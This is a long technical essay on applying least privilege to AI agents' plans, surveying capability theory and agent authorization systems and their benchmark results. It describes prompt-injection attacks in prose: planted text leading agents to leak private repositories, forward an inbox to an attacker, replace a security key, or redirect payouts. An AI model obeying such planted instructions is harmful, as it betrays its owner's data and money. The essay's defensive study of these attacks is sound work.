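# Applying the Principle of Least Privilege to an AI Agent's Plans

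## The principle of least privilege and how an agent makes a plan

The principle of least privilege is a computer security rule that a program or user should have only the rights needed for the current task. Engineers have applied it for half a century to operating systems, phone apps and cloud services, mostly by deciding which files, devices and services each program may access.

AI agents make least privilege harder to apply. An agent combines a language model with tools, such as a mail search or a payment service. It takes a goal in ordinary words, works out the steps and calls the tools to carry them out. The owner can choose the tools, but nobody specifies their order in advance, so the agent can combine individually permitted actions into a sequence the owner never wanted. Security researchers disagree on whether least privilege can rule out such sequences as well as tools. Some think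 that narrow enough permissions are sufficient. Others want to lock or check the plan before the agent acts on it, have the agent prefer plans that need fewer rights, or limit the consequences without changing the plan.

### The rule of 1975

The usual wording of the principle dates from 1975, when Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* that every program and every user should operate "using the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Saltzer had published a shorter list of principles in 1974, based on Multics, an early multi-user computer system, as Smith recounts in *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles* (2012). That earlier version, which Seamons (2017) reproduces in lecture slides, had "least amount of privilege" instead of "least set". The change matters for agents because two sets of privileges,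 unlike two amounts, cannot always be ranked.

Saltzer and Schroeder's first reason for least privilege was that a program with few rights can do little harm through accident or error. They also wanted fewer interactions among privileged programs, so that unintended uses of a privilege are less likely and an auditor investigating a misuse has fewer programs to examine. These reasons concern which programs hold which rights, not the order in which a program uses them.

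Least privilege is sixth in a list of eight design principles, and two of the others recur throughout the debate on agents. *Complete mediation* requires the system to check every access to every object, and to be wary of shortcuts that reuse the result of an earlier check. *Fail-safe defaults* means that the system refuses access unless a rule permits it. The argument for this was that an error in a mechanism that grants access tends to cause a refusal, which somebody soon notices, while an error in a mechanism that excludes people tends to let them in, which can go unnoticed in normal use. The remaining five are economy of mechanism (a small and simple design); open design (a design that stays safe when outsiders know it); separation of privilege (two keys held by different people, where feasible); least common mechanism (as little shared machinery between users as possible); and psychological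 acceptability (an interface that people will routinely use correctly).

Saltzer and Schroeder warned that their design principles were not "absolute rules". Breaking one is a symptom of possible trouble, and the designer should make sure that the trouble is unimportant or accounted for. In 2012, Smith counted least privilege among the five principles that still thrived. Smith did not include complete mediation, because no single device in a modern network has enough information to make access decisions.

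A system also needs a record of who may do what, and this record has two classic forms. An *access control list* belongs to an object, such as a file, and names the users and programs that may use it. A *capability* is an unforgeable reference, held by a user or program, that names an object and carries the right to use it. Both record *permissions*, which are rights to directly perform a given operation on a given object. A program's *authority* is wider because it covers every effect the program can cause, including effects through other programs it can influence.

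### How an agent arrives at its next step

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle inside Codex, OpenAI's programming agent. The agent puts the user's request into a prompt, together with instructions and a description of each available tool, and sends it to the model. The model returns either a final answer for the user or a request for a tool call, such as listing the files in a folder. If it returns a tool call, the agent runs the tool, adds the output to the prompt and queries the model again, repeating this until the model returns a final answer. A single user request can lead to hundreds of tool calls.

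Anthropic's *How the agent loop works*, written for developers who build on its Claude models, shows the same cycle with a request to fix the failing tests in a file. The model runs the tests, and three fail. It reads the source file and the test file, edits the source, runs the tests again, finds that they pass, and reports back. The edit depended on the failures and the contents of the files, so nobody, including the model, could have written it at the start.

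The *planner* is the part of the agent that makes these choices. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) defines it as the component, typically a language model inside a loop, that breaks a task down and selects the tool calls and their order. A *plan* is the steps, with their order and conditions, that the agent intends to carry out for a goal, and a *run* is the sequence of actions it actually carries out. One plan can lead to several runs. For example, "pay the bill, but if the balance is too low, send me an email" can lead to two. Some agents write the plan down. Codex has a built-in tool that the model uses to record and update a task plan, but it is one tool among others, and the loop that Bolin describes has no step that compares the next call with the recorded plan.

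Permissions apply after the agent requests a tool call and before the call runs. With Anthropic's kit, a developer can approve some tools in advance, block others and require consent for the rest. A rule can also restrict a single tool, for example by letting the command line run only certain kinds of commands. The developer can add code that intercepts each call before it runs, which is the natural place for a *monitor*, a component outside the agent that sees each action before it takes effect and can refuse it. This is a better starting point for complete mediation than the networks Smith was considering, but it doesn't guarantee that every action is covered. The sandbox in Codex, a closed-off area for running commands, covers only Codex's own command-line tool, and tools from outside servers have to enforce their own limits.

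When a rule blocks a call, the model receives a rejection message and, according to Anthropic, typically tries a different approach or reports that it could not proceed. The rule removes only one step, so the planner may still look for another way to reach the goal using the remaining steps.

### What has changed since 1975

In 1975, a program ordinarily came to the protection system with its steps already written. Someone could read the code, see what it needed and set its rights to match. Schneider, Morrisett and Harper's *A Language-Based Approach to Security* describes a program's text as a compact representation of everything the program might do. The program was therefore limited by its code as well as its rights. A payroll program with permission to write to every file in a folder would still, bugs aside, write only the files its code named, in the order its code gave.

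An agent's code does not show in advance which permissions it will need. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) contrasts agents with phone apps. A phone app has a fixed set of tasks, so its developer can ask for matching permissions and an analyst can check the code against them. An agent has no fixed program to analyse, because in effect it writes many programs as it goes. In the paper's example, a user tells a browser agent to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site for managing software projects, that the work is done. On that site, the agent needs only to reach the issue's page and write in the comment box, and nobody could have known this before the user typed the request. If the user next asks for a summary of the same issue, the agent no longer needs permission to write.

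Saltzer and Schroeder applied the principle of least privilege to users as well as programs, and a person at a terminal improvises much as an agent does, although the person can answer for the result. Fixed steps never guaranteed tight permissions either. Parkinson and colleagues cite a study in which 99.8% of 447,000 workflows on the code-hosting site GitHub, which are automated procedures written in advance, had more privilege than they needed. Agents inherited this problem and make it more dangerous, because a planner can use excess rights that a fixed script would have left alone.

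Today's agents mostly receive their rights before any plan exists. According to *PRISM* (2026), a proposal for matching tools to tasks, the mainstream arrangement is to authorise an agent once per session and list every tool of every connected server in the prompt. In a GitHub example from Parkinson and colleagues, a user connects a programming assistant with an ordinary access token. The assistant can then use about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, in every repository (project folder) that the user can reach. Two tools that can read from a single repository would be enough to summarise its open issues. An attacker exploited such excess rights in a reported case of *prompt injection*, in which an agent wrongly treats text in the material it reads as instructions. A message planted in a public repository led an agent to read its user's private repositories and publish them. A token with read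 access to only the one repository would have prevented this, but it would also have stopped the agent from doing the user's next task, repairing a failing build, which requires writing code.

*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) lists least privilege first among its principles for agents. It asks developers to limit an agent's permissions to what its current task requires and to adjust them as the task changes. How much this achieves depends on what the permissions prevent the agent from doing, even when they fit the task perfectly.

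### Runs, permissions and plan limits

Schneider and colleagues represent each execution of a program as a sequence of steps, and define a security policy as a condition on sets of such sequences. Access control is a special case that excludes only the sequences containing an unacceptable operation. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) applies the idea to agents. It treats a run as a finite sequence of actions, each of which passes its own check when the agent takes it, and contrasts these separate checks with a policy on what the user authorised for the whole episode.

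Let P be the set of actions an agent has permission to take, and let R(P) be the set of all possible runs, where a run is a finite sequence of actions from P in any order, with repeats allowed. If the permissions stay fixed during the run and each check depends only on the current action, then P allows every run in R(P). A *plan limit* is a rule that allows only some of these runs, written as a set L ⊆ R(P). (The term is a working label, not an established one.) The *plan space* is the set of all plans the agent could form and carry out with P.

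Suppose an owner tells an AI assistant to pay the electricity bill, and the assistant is allowed to search the owner's mail, open attachments, check the bank balance, make payments and send emails. The owner expects it to search for the bill, open it and pay it. But the five permitted actions can form 780 different sequences of up to four steps (5 + 25 + 125 + 625). In one of them, the assistant searches the mail, opens an attachment and sends an email, which could pass a private document to a stranger.

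Least privilege removes that run. The job doesn't require checking the balance or sending email, so the owner can remove those actions and leave only search, open and pay. The assistant needs all three if the amount and the account number are in the attachment. These three actions still allow 3 + 9 + 27 + 81 = 120 runs of up to four steps. One is the run the owner intended. Another is search, open, pay, pay, which pays the bill twice. The assistant pays more than once in 41 of the 120 runs, and in some it pays before opening anything.

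The count includes every run the permissions allow, though many would fail in practice or do nothing of interest. Real agents also take far more than four steps. Bolin mentions hundreds of calls, and five actions already allow about 10^70 runs of up to a hundred steps.

A plan limit further restricts the runs that the permissions allow. Suppose the owner adds a rule that the agent may pay at most once, and only after it has searched and then opened an attachment. Of the 120 runs, 37 comply. In 30 of those, the agent makes no payment. In the other seven, it pays once after the required steps, sometimes with a harmless extra search or a second look at the attachment.

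| Rule on the assistant | Runs of up to four steps that it allows |
|---|---|
| Five permissions: search, open, check balance, pay, send | 780 |
| Three permissions: search, open, pay | 120 |
| Three permissions, and pay at most once, after search and then open | 37 |
| One permission at a time: search, then open, then pay, then none | 3 |

In the last row, the principle also limits when the assistant holds each right. In the restatement by Schneider and colleagues, each party should have the minimum access necessary "throughout execution", which suggests that a right should lapse once the job no longer needs it. If the assistant holds only the right to search, then only the right to open, then only the right to pay, and after that nothing, the only possible runs are the intended one and the two that stop partway through it. Permissions that change at every step can therefore restrict the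 assistant as tightly as a very strict plan limit. But someone has to know the plan to write the schedule of permissions, and an agent's plan emerges as it works.

Even that schedule doesn't specify whom the assistant pays. "Pay" covers a separate action for each payee and amount. If the owner's account has twenty saved payees, the single intended run becomes twenty runs with the same sequence of steps, and nineteen of them send the money to the wrong party. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026), a survey, recommends applying least privilege at several levels: which tools the agent can see, whether the current step needs the tool, which arguments the call carries (recipient, path, amount), how much data comes back to the model, and what a helper agent inherits. The definitions still hold if P contains "pay the electricity company up to 90 euros" instead of "pay". But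 the permissions become much harder to write in practice, because whoever writes them must know the payee and the approximate amount before the assistant has found the bill.

### Minimal sets and least sets

So far the assistant has had one way to pay the bill. Suppose it can also sign in to the supplier's website and pay there with a saved card. Those two actions are enough without the other five, so either of two different sets of permissions now lets it pay the bill: search, open and pay, or sign in and pay by card.

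A set of permissions is *sufficient* if some run built from it reaches the goal. A sufficient set is *minimal* if removing any permission makes it insufficient, and *least* if every other sufficient set contains it. Both of the assistant's sets are minimal, but neither contains the other, so there is no least set. The website route has two actions and allows 30 runs of up to four steps, while the mail route has three actions and allows 120. These counts are not enough to choose between the routes, because the website route gives the assistant free use of a customer account and a stored card, whereas the mail route opens the owner's correspondence and bank account. An owner who worries about private letters will choose differently from one who worries about the card. Saltzer's 1974 phrase "amount of privilege" would require one of the two sets to carry less privilege than the other.

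*Are You Still the Agent I Authorized?* (Zhang and Zhang, 2026) gives the general version of this in its appendix. It defines what a task needs as the family of all sets of effects that are sufficient for at least one plan to complete the task, rather than as a single minimum, because different plans may need sets that can't be ranked. The family also changes as the work proceeds. When a programming agent moves from testing its code to publishing it, the task requires a new right, though the agent and its tools haven't changed.

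A plan with fixed steps can still have several minimal sets of permissions. Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, examined Google's and Microsoft's published tables of which permissions authorise which operations. The tables cover some 23,900 methods at Google and 22,300 entries for Microsoft Graph, the interface to Microsoft's mail, files and user directories. Xu counted one grant as smaller than another only if it authorises a proper subset of the other's operations. Between 29.8% and 33.3% of the Graph tasks, depending on the type of authorisation, had no unique minimum, compared with 3.2% of the Google tasks. For example, either of two permissions lets a program read the metadata of a project in BigQuery, Google's data warehouse, and neither is smaller than the other. One is a BigQuery permission that covers 286 methods, 144 of which change something. The other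 is a read-only permission that covers 565 methods across many more services, and Xu classes 61 of those methods as changing something.

Xu generated the tasks from the structure of the tables, so the percentages describe the two catalogues and do not show how often a working agent runs into the problem. The tenfold difference between the companies suggests that much of the problem comes from how each vendor divides its permissions. Xu notes that a vendor could in principle remove every such tie by adding a permission that covers only what the competing grants have in common, since the task lies inside that overlap. This would not work for the electricity bill, because its two routes consist of different actions. However finely the bank, the mail provider and the supplier divide their permissions, neither route's set will contain the other's. Someone has to choose the route, and with it much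 of the plan, before least privilege can determine a single set of permissions to grant.

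## The view that narrow authority is enough

The simplest view of least privilege is that once the owner has chosen a route for paying the electricity bill, the plan needs no further attention. If the assistant can cause only the effects that the job requires, every plan it could carry out would be acceptable. Even if it misreads the request or follows instructions that an attacker hid in an email, the worst result is one the owner has accepted in advance. Noyan argues in *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* that an agent cannot misuse a credential it doesn't have, however it reasons and however good it is at evasion.

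The view is attractive because it doesn't require anyone to understand the planner. A language model's choices vary from run to run and are hard to predict, but the list of what it can touch is short, and ordinary code can check that list the same way every time. The argument is also valid, since if every outcome the agent can bring about is acceptable, every plan is too, and limiting its plans is unnecessary. The dispute is over whether an agent can have enough authority to do a useful job without being able to do that job badly.

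### Names and ambient authority

The view grew out of an operating system design that Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn published in 1966, nine years before Saltzer and Schroeder's principles. In 2003, Miller and Shapiro's *Paradigm Regained* argued that this design was stronger than its critics supposed. In their account, a program can act on something outside itself only through a capability. The program gets its capabilities from whoever starts it, from other programs that already hold them, or by creating new objects.

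Most computers work differently, as Miller and Shapiro show with two Unix commands that both copy a file. The first is `cp foo.txt bar.txt`. The shell, the program that reads what the user types, passes `cp` the two file names as text, and `cp` has to find and open the files itself. It must therefore be able to read and write any file the user might name. This authority is *ambient*, meaning that `cp` has it merely because of whose account it runs under.

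The second command is `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`. Here the shell opens both files and gives `cat` two open connections, one for reading and one for writing. On an ordinary Unix system `cat` still runs with all of the user's authority, but an operating system could remove everything except those two connections and the copy would still succeed. Under the same restriction `cp` couldn't open either file, because a program that receives file names needs nearly all of the user's authority over files.

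In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller, Yee and Shapiro trace the difference to where a system records permissions. An access control list points from a file to its users, so programs need a separate set of names to identify files. A capability points from the program to the file, so the program needs no separate name for it. Access control lists also encourage coarse divisions, because a list has to name its subjects in advance. Running programs come and go too quickly for that, so in practice the subjects are user accounts. A capability system can treat each running program as a separate subject.

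When naming a resource is separate from having the right to use it, a program can become a *confused deputy*, Norm Hardy's 1988 term for a program that someone tricks into misusing its own privileges. Suppose a backup service runs under an administrator's account and copies any file to any destination a user names. A user with no right to change the payroll file could name it as the destination, and the service would overwrite it, because the service has that right. If the user instead had to open the destination file and pass the service that open connection, the trick would fail, because the user cannot open the payroll file for writing.

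An agent is an unusually easy deputy to confuse because it reads emails and web pages written by strangers while holding its owner's rights. An account number in a stranger's email looks just like one from the owner, so if the payment tool accepts account numbers, the stranger can redirect the money. If the tool accepts only capabilities, which are unforgeable references, the stranger can do much less, because an email cannot contain one. The attacker can still try to make the agent use a capability it already holds, for instance to pay the landlord instead of the electricity company. Capabilities limit a confused agent to choosing among things the owner has already handed over, so the view also requires those things to be few and specific.

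### Permission and authority

Miller and Shapiro's main distinction is between permission and authority. In their example, Alice has permission to read a password file and Bob does not. If Alice sends Bob copies of the text, Bob has the authority to read the file without permission. They say it is unclear whether Saltzer and Schroeder's principle is best read as least permission or least authority, and that the difference is enormous.

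An assistant that holds only search, open and pay has the least set of permissions for its route to paying the electricity bill, but it can still pay the bill twice. It follows the principle if the principle concerns permissions, but breaks it if the principle concerns authority, because a second payment is an effect that the job doesn't need. The view is much stronger on the authority reading, but somebody must then work out what a given set of permissions lets a program bring about, and that depends on what all the other programs do.

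The cautious way to work this out is to assume that every program is hostile and to look only at which programs hold references to which. If no chain of references connects Bob to the file, Bob can never read it. If there is a chain, the answer is only "maybe". (Some systems have rules for passing on rights that make the question undecidable.) An analyst who also knows how some of the programs behave can often turn a "maybe" into a "no". The three sets involved are nested:

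effects that can really occur ⊆ effects possible given the known behaviour ⊆ effects possible given the references alone

Miller and Shapiro apply this to an old problem in military computing, in which a program cleared for secrets may send data to a program cleared for top secrets but must receive nothing back. They connect the programs through two small objects that share a stored number. The lower program can reach only the object that writes the number, and the higher program can reach only the object that reads it. From the references alone, it is possible that the lower program could pass a capability to the writing object, the higher program could somehow obtain it, and the two programs could then build a return channel. The objects' code prevents this because the writing object accepts only whole numbers and the reading object only returns them. The lower program can therefore send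 numbers but not capabilities, and the higher program can send nothing back.

An owner who wants a tight bound on an agent's authority has to get it from the tools around the planner. The tools are ordinary code whose behaviour can be relied on, unlike the planner's.

### A payment that works once

The double payment looks like a counterexample to this view, since the assistant needs all three of its permissions and can still do harm with them. A defender would answer that the "pay" permission was too broad, and that the assistant should have received permission to make only one payment of a set amount to one company.

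Miller and Shapiro describe a pattern from 1974, Redell's *caretaker*, that makes such a right easy to build. A caretaker is a small object that stands between a program and a resource and forwards requests until somebody switches it off. A single-use capability is a reference to a caretaker that switches itself off:

```
used = false

pay():
    if used: refuse
    used = true
    bank.transfer(to: electricity company, amount: 84.60)
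```

The assistant can call `pay()` but cannot reach anything behind it, so it cannot change the payee or amount, or reset the flag. If the connection to the bank fails halfway, the assistant cannot try again and the owner has to issue a new capability. If the last two lines were reversed, a retry could pay twice.

This removes the 41 runs that pay more than once, leaving 79 of the 120 possible runs of up to four steps using search, open and pay. In some of the 79, the assistant pays before opening the bill, which is harmless if the payee and amount are already fixed. However, the owner has to know the amount before the assistant has found the bill.

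Capabilities can deal with this too, because a tool can return a capability as its result. Suppose the assistant starts with only the search tool. Each search result comes with a capability to open that message, and opening the electricity bill returns a single-use capability to pay the amount printed on it. The assistant cannot pay before opening the bill because it does not yet have that capability. Only 21 of the 120 runs are now possible, all of them among the 37 that the owner's rule on payments allows. This works only if opening the same bill twice returns the same capability, because otherwise the assistant could pay as often as it opened the bill.

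A capability with built-in behaviour can therefore limit how many times actions happen and in what order, so the view is stronger than a count of permissions suggests. But a capability that records whether it has been used is already enforcing a limit on the plan, and somebody had to think of that limit when writing the tool. If the owner leaves both payment routes open, with one single-use capability for the bank and another for the card stored on the supplier's website, the assistant can pay once by each route. To prevent this, the two capabilities have to share a flag, which requires whoever writes them to foresee the combination.

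### How agent systems narrow authority

Several recent systems try to fit an agent's authority to each task automatically. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) expresses that authority as a list of rules about tool calls. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and sets conditions on its arguments, such as a maximum value, a list of acceptable recipients or a text pattern. The system applies "forbid" rules before "allow" rules and blocks any call that no rule matches.

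A language model writes the first policy from the user's request alone, before the agent reads any outside data. In the paper's example, the user asks the agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice, and the first policy allows only a search for that email. The to-do list asks for a summary of recent mail, posted to the user's Slack account, so the model proposes a second policy that adds the tools for this. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, a third policy restricts messages to that name. One of the recent emails contains a planted instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. The agent tries to follow it, but Progent blocks the call because no rule allows the agent to send email.

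An attacker might also try to influence the policy updates. Let A(P) be the set of tool calls that policy P allows. Before a new policy P′ takes effect, an SMT solver, which is a program that decides whether logical formulas can be satisfied, tests whether A(P′) ⊆ A(P). If it is, the new policy only removes rights and applies at once. Otherwise it needs approval, from a person or from a rule set beforehand. Between approvals the agent's authority can therefore only shrink:

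A(P₀) ⊇ A(P₁) ⊇ A(P₂) ⊇ …

In principle this could also prevent the double payment, because the model could propose a policy without the payment tool after the first payment. In practice it may not, because the model first decides whether a call could make an update necessary. Shi and colleagues give writing files and sending emails as examples of calls that don't require an update, and a payment looks similar to those.

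Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, work with the permissions that online services already offer. Most of these use OAuth, a standard that lets a user give one application limited access to an account on another, and they divide access into *scopes*, which are named bundles of operations. MiniScope places one scope below another if its operations are a subset of the other's. The agent submits the calls it intends to make, and a solver looks for the cheapest set of scopes that covers them:

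minimise Σ cost(v) · x(v), so that at least one chosen scope authorises each intended call

Here x(v) is 1 if the solver chooses scope v and 0 otherwise, and cost(v) is the number of operations that v authorises. Choosing the smallest scope for each call separately may not give the best result, because scopes overlap. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 operations can be reached by more than one path through the hierarchy. The user then either refuses any new scopes or grants them once, for the session, or permanently. A checker compares every call with what the user has granted and keeps the real credentials away from the agent.

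The cost formula ranks permissions that the subset relation leaves unranked. Xu points out that MiniScope doesn't discuss whether its optimum is unique, and the formula's ranking can be questionable. In Xu's BigQuery example, when operations are counted over Google's whole catalogue, the formula ranks a permission that covers fewer operations, half of which change something, above a broader read-only permission. Many owners would choose the read-only permission instead.

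The closest of these systems to the capability tradition is the one that Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, describe. It issues a signed token for each call the agent proposes, naming the agent, the session, the action, the resource and a declared purpose, along with an expiry time and a number of uses. A gateway checks the token before it forwards the call. To get a token, the agent has to meet seven conditions:

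- the system has not isolated the agent for bad behaviour;
- the requested right exists in the catalogue;
- sensitive arguments have acceptable origins;
- the policy permits the declared purpose;
- the agent's trust score is high enough;
- the agent already holds any tokens that this right depends on;
- the new right does not form a forbidden combination with rights the agent holds.

In the example policy for a bank, a token to send money lasts 30 seconds and works once. The agent must already hold a token to read the balance, and the recipient must not come solely from untrusted text. This resembles the single-use capability, but the one-use limit applies to each token separately. None of the seven conditions counts earlier payments, so they don't by themselves stop an agent from asking for a second token and paying the same company again. An agent can also hold a token to read the balance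 without having read it. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, which reviews 89 sources, lists limits on the combined effect of an agent's actions among the main unresolved gaps in the field.

The trust score can also penalize honest agents. By default it starts at 0.8, exactly the level the bank policy requires for sending money. One refused call lowers it by 30%, to 0.56, and each normal outcome then closes only 1% of the remaining gap to full trust. At that rate, an agent needs 79 normal outcomes after a single refusal before it can send money again.

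Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, enforce the limits before anything runs. In their system, TACIT, the agent writes short Scala programs instead of calling tools one at a time, and the compiler tracks which capabilities each piece of code can use. A function that writes to file `f` has a type that includes `f`. The type of a *pure* function includes no capabilities, so the function can calculate but cannot write a file or contact a server.

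In TACIT, secret data arrives in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent's code can process the contents only by passing a pure function to the wrapper, which returns the result wrapped as well. A program that shortens a secret report therefore compiles, but one that copies the report into a public file does not. Rules about single calls have trouble expressing this restriction, since the agent is allowed both to read secrets and to write public files. File access also ends with the block of code that requested it, because the compiler rejects any result that would carry the capability out of the block. TACIT inspects the agent's steps before they run, so it is as good an example of checking a plan as of narrowing authority.

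A whole task can also be too large a unit for granting permissions. In *Authority Is Not a String*, Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026) consider a programming job that one agent divides among three others: a runner that runs the tests, a patcher that edits the code and a verifier that runs the tests again. The job requires writing to source files, so a policy that covers the whole job lets the runner write to them too. But the runner reads the test output, where an attacker may have planted an instruction to replace a security key. Their system, CapScope, limits the permissions for the whole job before any agent has read the contents of a file, using only the user's request and the file names. It then gives each agent only the permissions within that limit that its subtask needs. The runner can run tests but cannot write to files, so the planted instruction fails even though the patcher may edit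 the file it targets.

### What the tests found

Most of the evidence comes from tests of prompt injection. Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, and Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on it. AgentDojo simulates banking, Slack, travel booking and office work, and plants hostile instructions in the data that the tools return. The full benchmark has 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacked ones. Shi and colleagues left out two kinds of travel attack, and had Progent approve every request for a wider policy, to imitate a careless user. They also used ASB, a benchmark with ten agent scenarios. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote AgentCap's policies by hand from the tool descriptions and the ordinary tasks, and froze them before testing. They also used InjecAgent, which has 1,054 attacks.

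Odersky and colleagues built a software project with a folder of secrets. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 injections and added 11 requests for the secrets, made openly or under a false identity. They ran all 131 trials on each model, with and without the wrapper. Bouras and colleagues combined each of five small repair jobs with each of five hiding places for the injection and ran each combination three times, for a total of 75 runs for each way of assigning authority.

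| System and test | Successful attacks, without and with the system | Ordinary tasks completed | Overhead |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent, AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 39.9%, 1.0% | 68.0% in Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao's rerun, against 81.4% unprotected | 6% of policy updates need approval |
| Progent, ASB, GPT-4o | 70.3%, 3.9% | Comparable to no defence | |
| AgentCap, AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6%, 5.1% | 3.1 points lower | Under 0.2 milliseconds per check |
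| AgentCap, AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2%, 0% | 7.2 points lower | Same |
| AgentCap, InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2%, 8.6% | 11.7 points lower | Same |
| AgentCap, InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0%, 0% | 5.9 points lower | Same |
| TACIT, secrets test, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5%, 0% | 99.2%, against 83.3% without the wrapper | Compiling takes under a second |
| TACIT, secrets test, MiniMax M2.5 | 8.4%, 0% | 90.0%, against 88.3% without the wrapper | Same |
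| CapScope, code repair, Qwen3.5-Flash | 47 of 75, 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 repairs under attack, against 72 | 316 seconds per run, against 145 |

The rows can't be ranked against each other, since even the two AgentDojo tests of GPT-4o started from different rates. The results do all go in the same direction, and CapScope's records show why. With CapScope in place, the model still proposed the attacker's action in 34 of the 75 runs, but the action took effect in only three, as the view predicts. Giving all the agents on a repair job one shared policy, written for that job, still let 33 of 75 attacks through. CapScope runs took longer partly because agents kept trying after a refusal.

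TACIT's results were also less dependent on the model. Without the wrapper, MiniMax M2.5 leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 malicious requests and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 2, but neither leaked any with it. Writing Scala instead of calling tools did little harm to performance. On simulated customer service, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 points higher with Scala, though between 0.3% and 7.9% of the programs needed another attempt before they compiled. On a set of real programming problems, the score of the one model tested fell from 43.3% to 41.7%.

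How much useful work these restrictions prevent is less settled. Shi and colleagues report that Progent maintained the agent's success on ordinary tasks. In the rerun, its policies often blocked legitimate calls because they restricted arguments to values that the model had anticipated from the request. AgentCap did better, but the researchers wrote its policies with the benchmark's tasks in front of them, while an owner writing a policy for next week's errands has no such list.

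Zhu and colleagues measured the size of the permissions MiniScope grants, the delay it adds and the effort it requires from users. They generated requests for ten real services, including Gmail, Slack and Dropbox. MiniScope added a delay of 1–6%. When language models chose the permissions instead of the solver, commercial models reached 70–83% optimality and open models reached 20–34%. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, the confirmation rate ranged from 18% to 60%, depending on the type of user.

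Those confirmations matter because MiniScope treats the user's answer as correct. Parkinson and colleagues cite a vendor's report that users of its programming agent approved 93% of permission prompts. Progent depends less on careful users. Its first policy, without updates, reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5%, and the rate was 1.0% even when every later expansion was approved. It fell to zero when a careful person reviewed the first policy and every expansion.

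These tests only partly support the view. The attackers mostly wanted something the task didn't need, such as a transfer to a stranger or a copy of a secret, and narrow authority is well suited to blocking that. The results do not show how often an agent uses the rights it needs in a harmful order or too many times, for example by paying the right company twice.

### A visible tool is not an authorised call

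Many agents in use have much weaker protection than any of these systems. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined the public code of three common agent toolkits: LangChain with LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and Stripe's Agent Toolkit. The "capability gate" in the title is a list of the tools an agent can see, and has little to do with an unforgeable reference. All three toolkits let a developer restrict that list, but by default none of them checks the values in a call against a policy and refuses the call when no rule allows them.

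Mellafe Zuvic demonstrated the gap with LangChain and a mock merchant system. A scripted model output contained a call to change the merchant's payout account to an attacker's. LangChain carried out the change because the tool existed and the account number had the right format. In a companion test of 27 models, the cheaper ones attempted the unauthorised action in 60% of trials on average, and the flagship models in 19%.

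Mellafe Zuvic's remedy, ScopeGate, is a monitor that refuses any call that fails one of four checks. The tool must be on a list, the restricted arguments must have approved values, and the amount must be a finite number no higher than a ceiling. If repeating the call would be dangerous, it must also include an idempotency key, a label that lets a payment service recognise a repeated request and avoid paying again. ScopeGate checks only that the key is present, so the service must recognise the repeat itself.

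An early version of ScopeGate had a flaw that illustrates Saltzer and Schroeder's rule of fail-safe defaults. It checked whether the amount was above the ceiling, so the special value "not a number" passed, because any comparison with it gives "false". The corrected version checks whether the amount is within the range, so the same value fails. It stopped all 48 prepared attempts to bypass it and 29 unauthorised calls from an attacking model that could read the reasons for each refusal. In a separate test, it allowed all ten legitimate calls.

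This objection refutes the loose form of the view, that an agent with few tools has little authority, but not the strict form. A capability to pay the electricity company 84.60 euros once already specifies the payee, the amount and the number of payments, so whoever issued it has authorised the call in detail. Progent and AgentCap check each call's arguments as well as the tool's name.

Mellafe Zuvic also requires that no part of the policy come from a model's output at any stage, because text that corrupts the call could corrupt the policy too. Progent and CapScope both break this rule by having a model draft the policy, but the model writes the first draft before it sees any untrusted text, and ordinary code controls what happens afterwards. The draft can still be wrong without an attacker's help. In two of CapScope's seven failed repairs, the draft policy left out permission to edit the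 file that needed editing. Hand-written policies avoid this problem, but they suit a merchant with one payout account better than an assistant whose tasks change constantly.

*Trust Is Not a Score* (2026) accepts that Progent and MiniScope give a real guarantee at the boundary they control, but finds that guarantee limited in scope. A call can pass every check even when it is based on outdated evidence, as when the assistant pays a bill that the supplier has since corrected. The designers of these systems acknowledge similar limits. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within the least privilege for the task, such as a seller tricking the agent into preferring one product among several valid ones. Zhu and colleagues exclude attacks that change the plan but use only scopes the user has already granted. Bouras and colleagues concede that a permitted read followed by a permitted write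 can still move data to the wrong place. TACIT shows that a sufficiently narrow capability can prevent even that, provided someone has marked the data as secret before the agent reads it.

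## The view that the plan itself must be fixed or checked

An assistant that may search mail, open attachments and pay bills can use those permissions to do its job or to do damage. Which it does depends on the order of its actions, how often it repeats them, which ones it combines and where it gets the values it passes to each tool. People who hold this view conclude that owners should authorise plans, because a list of permissions leaves out what makes a plan dangerous. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) states that "security is a property of the entire execution that a plan creates". OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) makes the weaker claim that a valid credential can give access to a system without establishing which actions anyone has authorised.

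*Architecting Secure AI Agents* (Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues, 2026) treats a security policy as a test on each step together with the steps before it. Such a test permits only certain plans, much as a plan limit L permits only some of the runs in R(P). An owner can fix one plan before the agent reads anything, check the values that flow through the plan, or ban certain combinations of actions whatever the plan is.

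### Planning before reading

In the ordinary agent loop, the model reads the output of one tool before it chooses the next, so a stranger's email can influence the choice. A design called *plan-then-execute* removes that influence. A planner sees only the user's request and writes out all the steps. An executor then carries them out in order, and nothing it reads can change the list.

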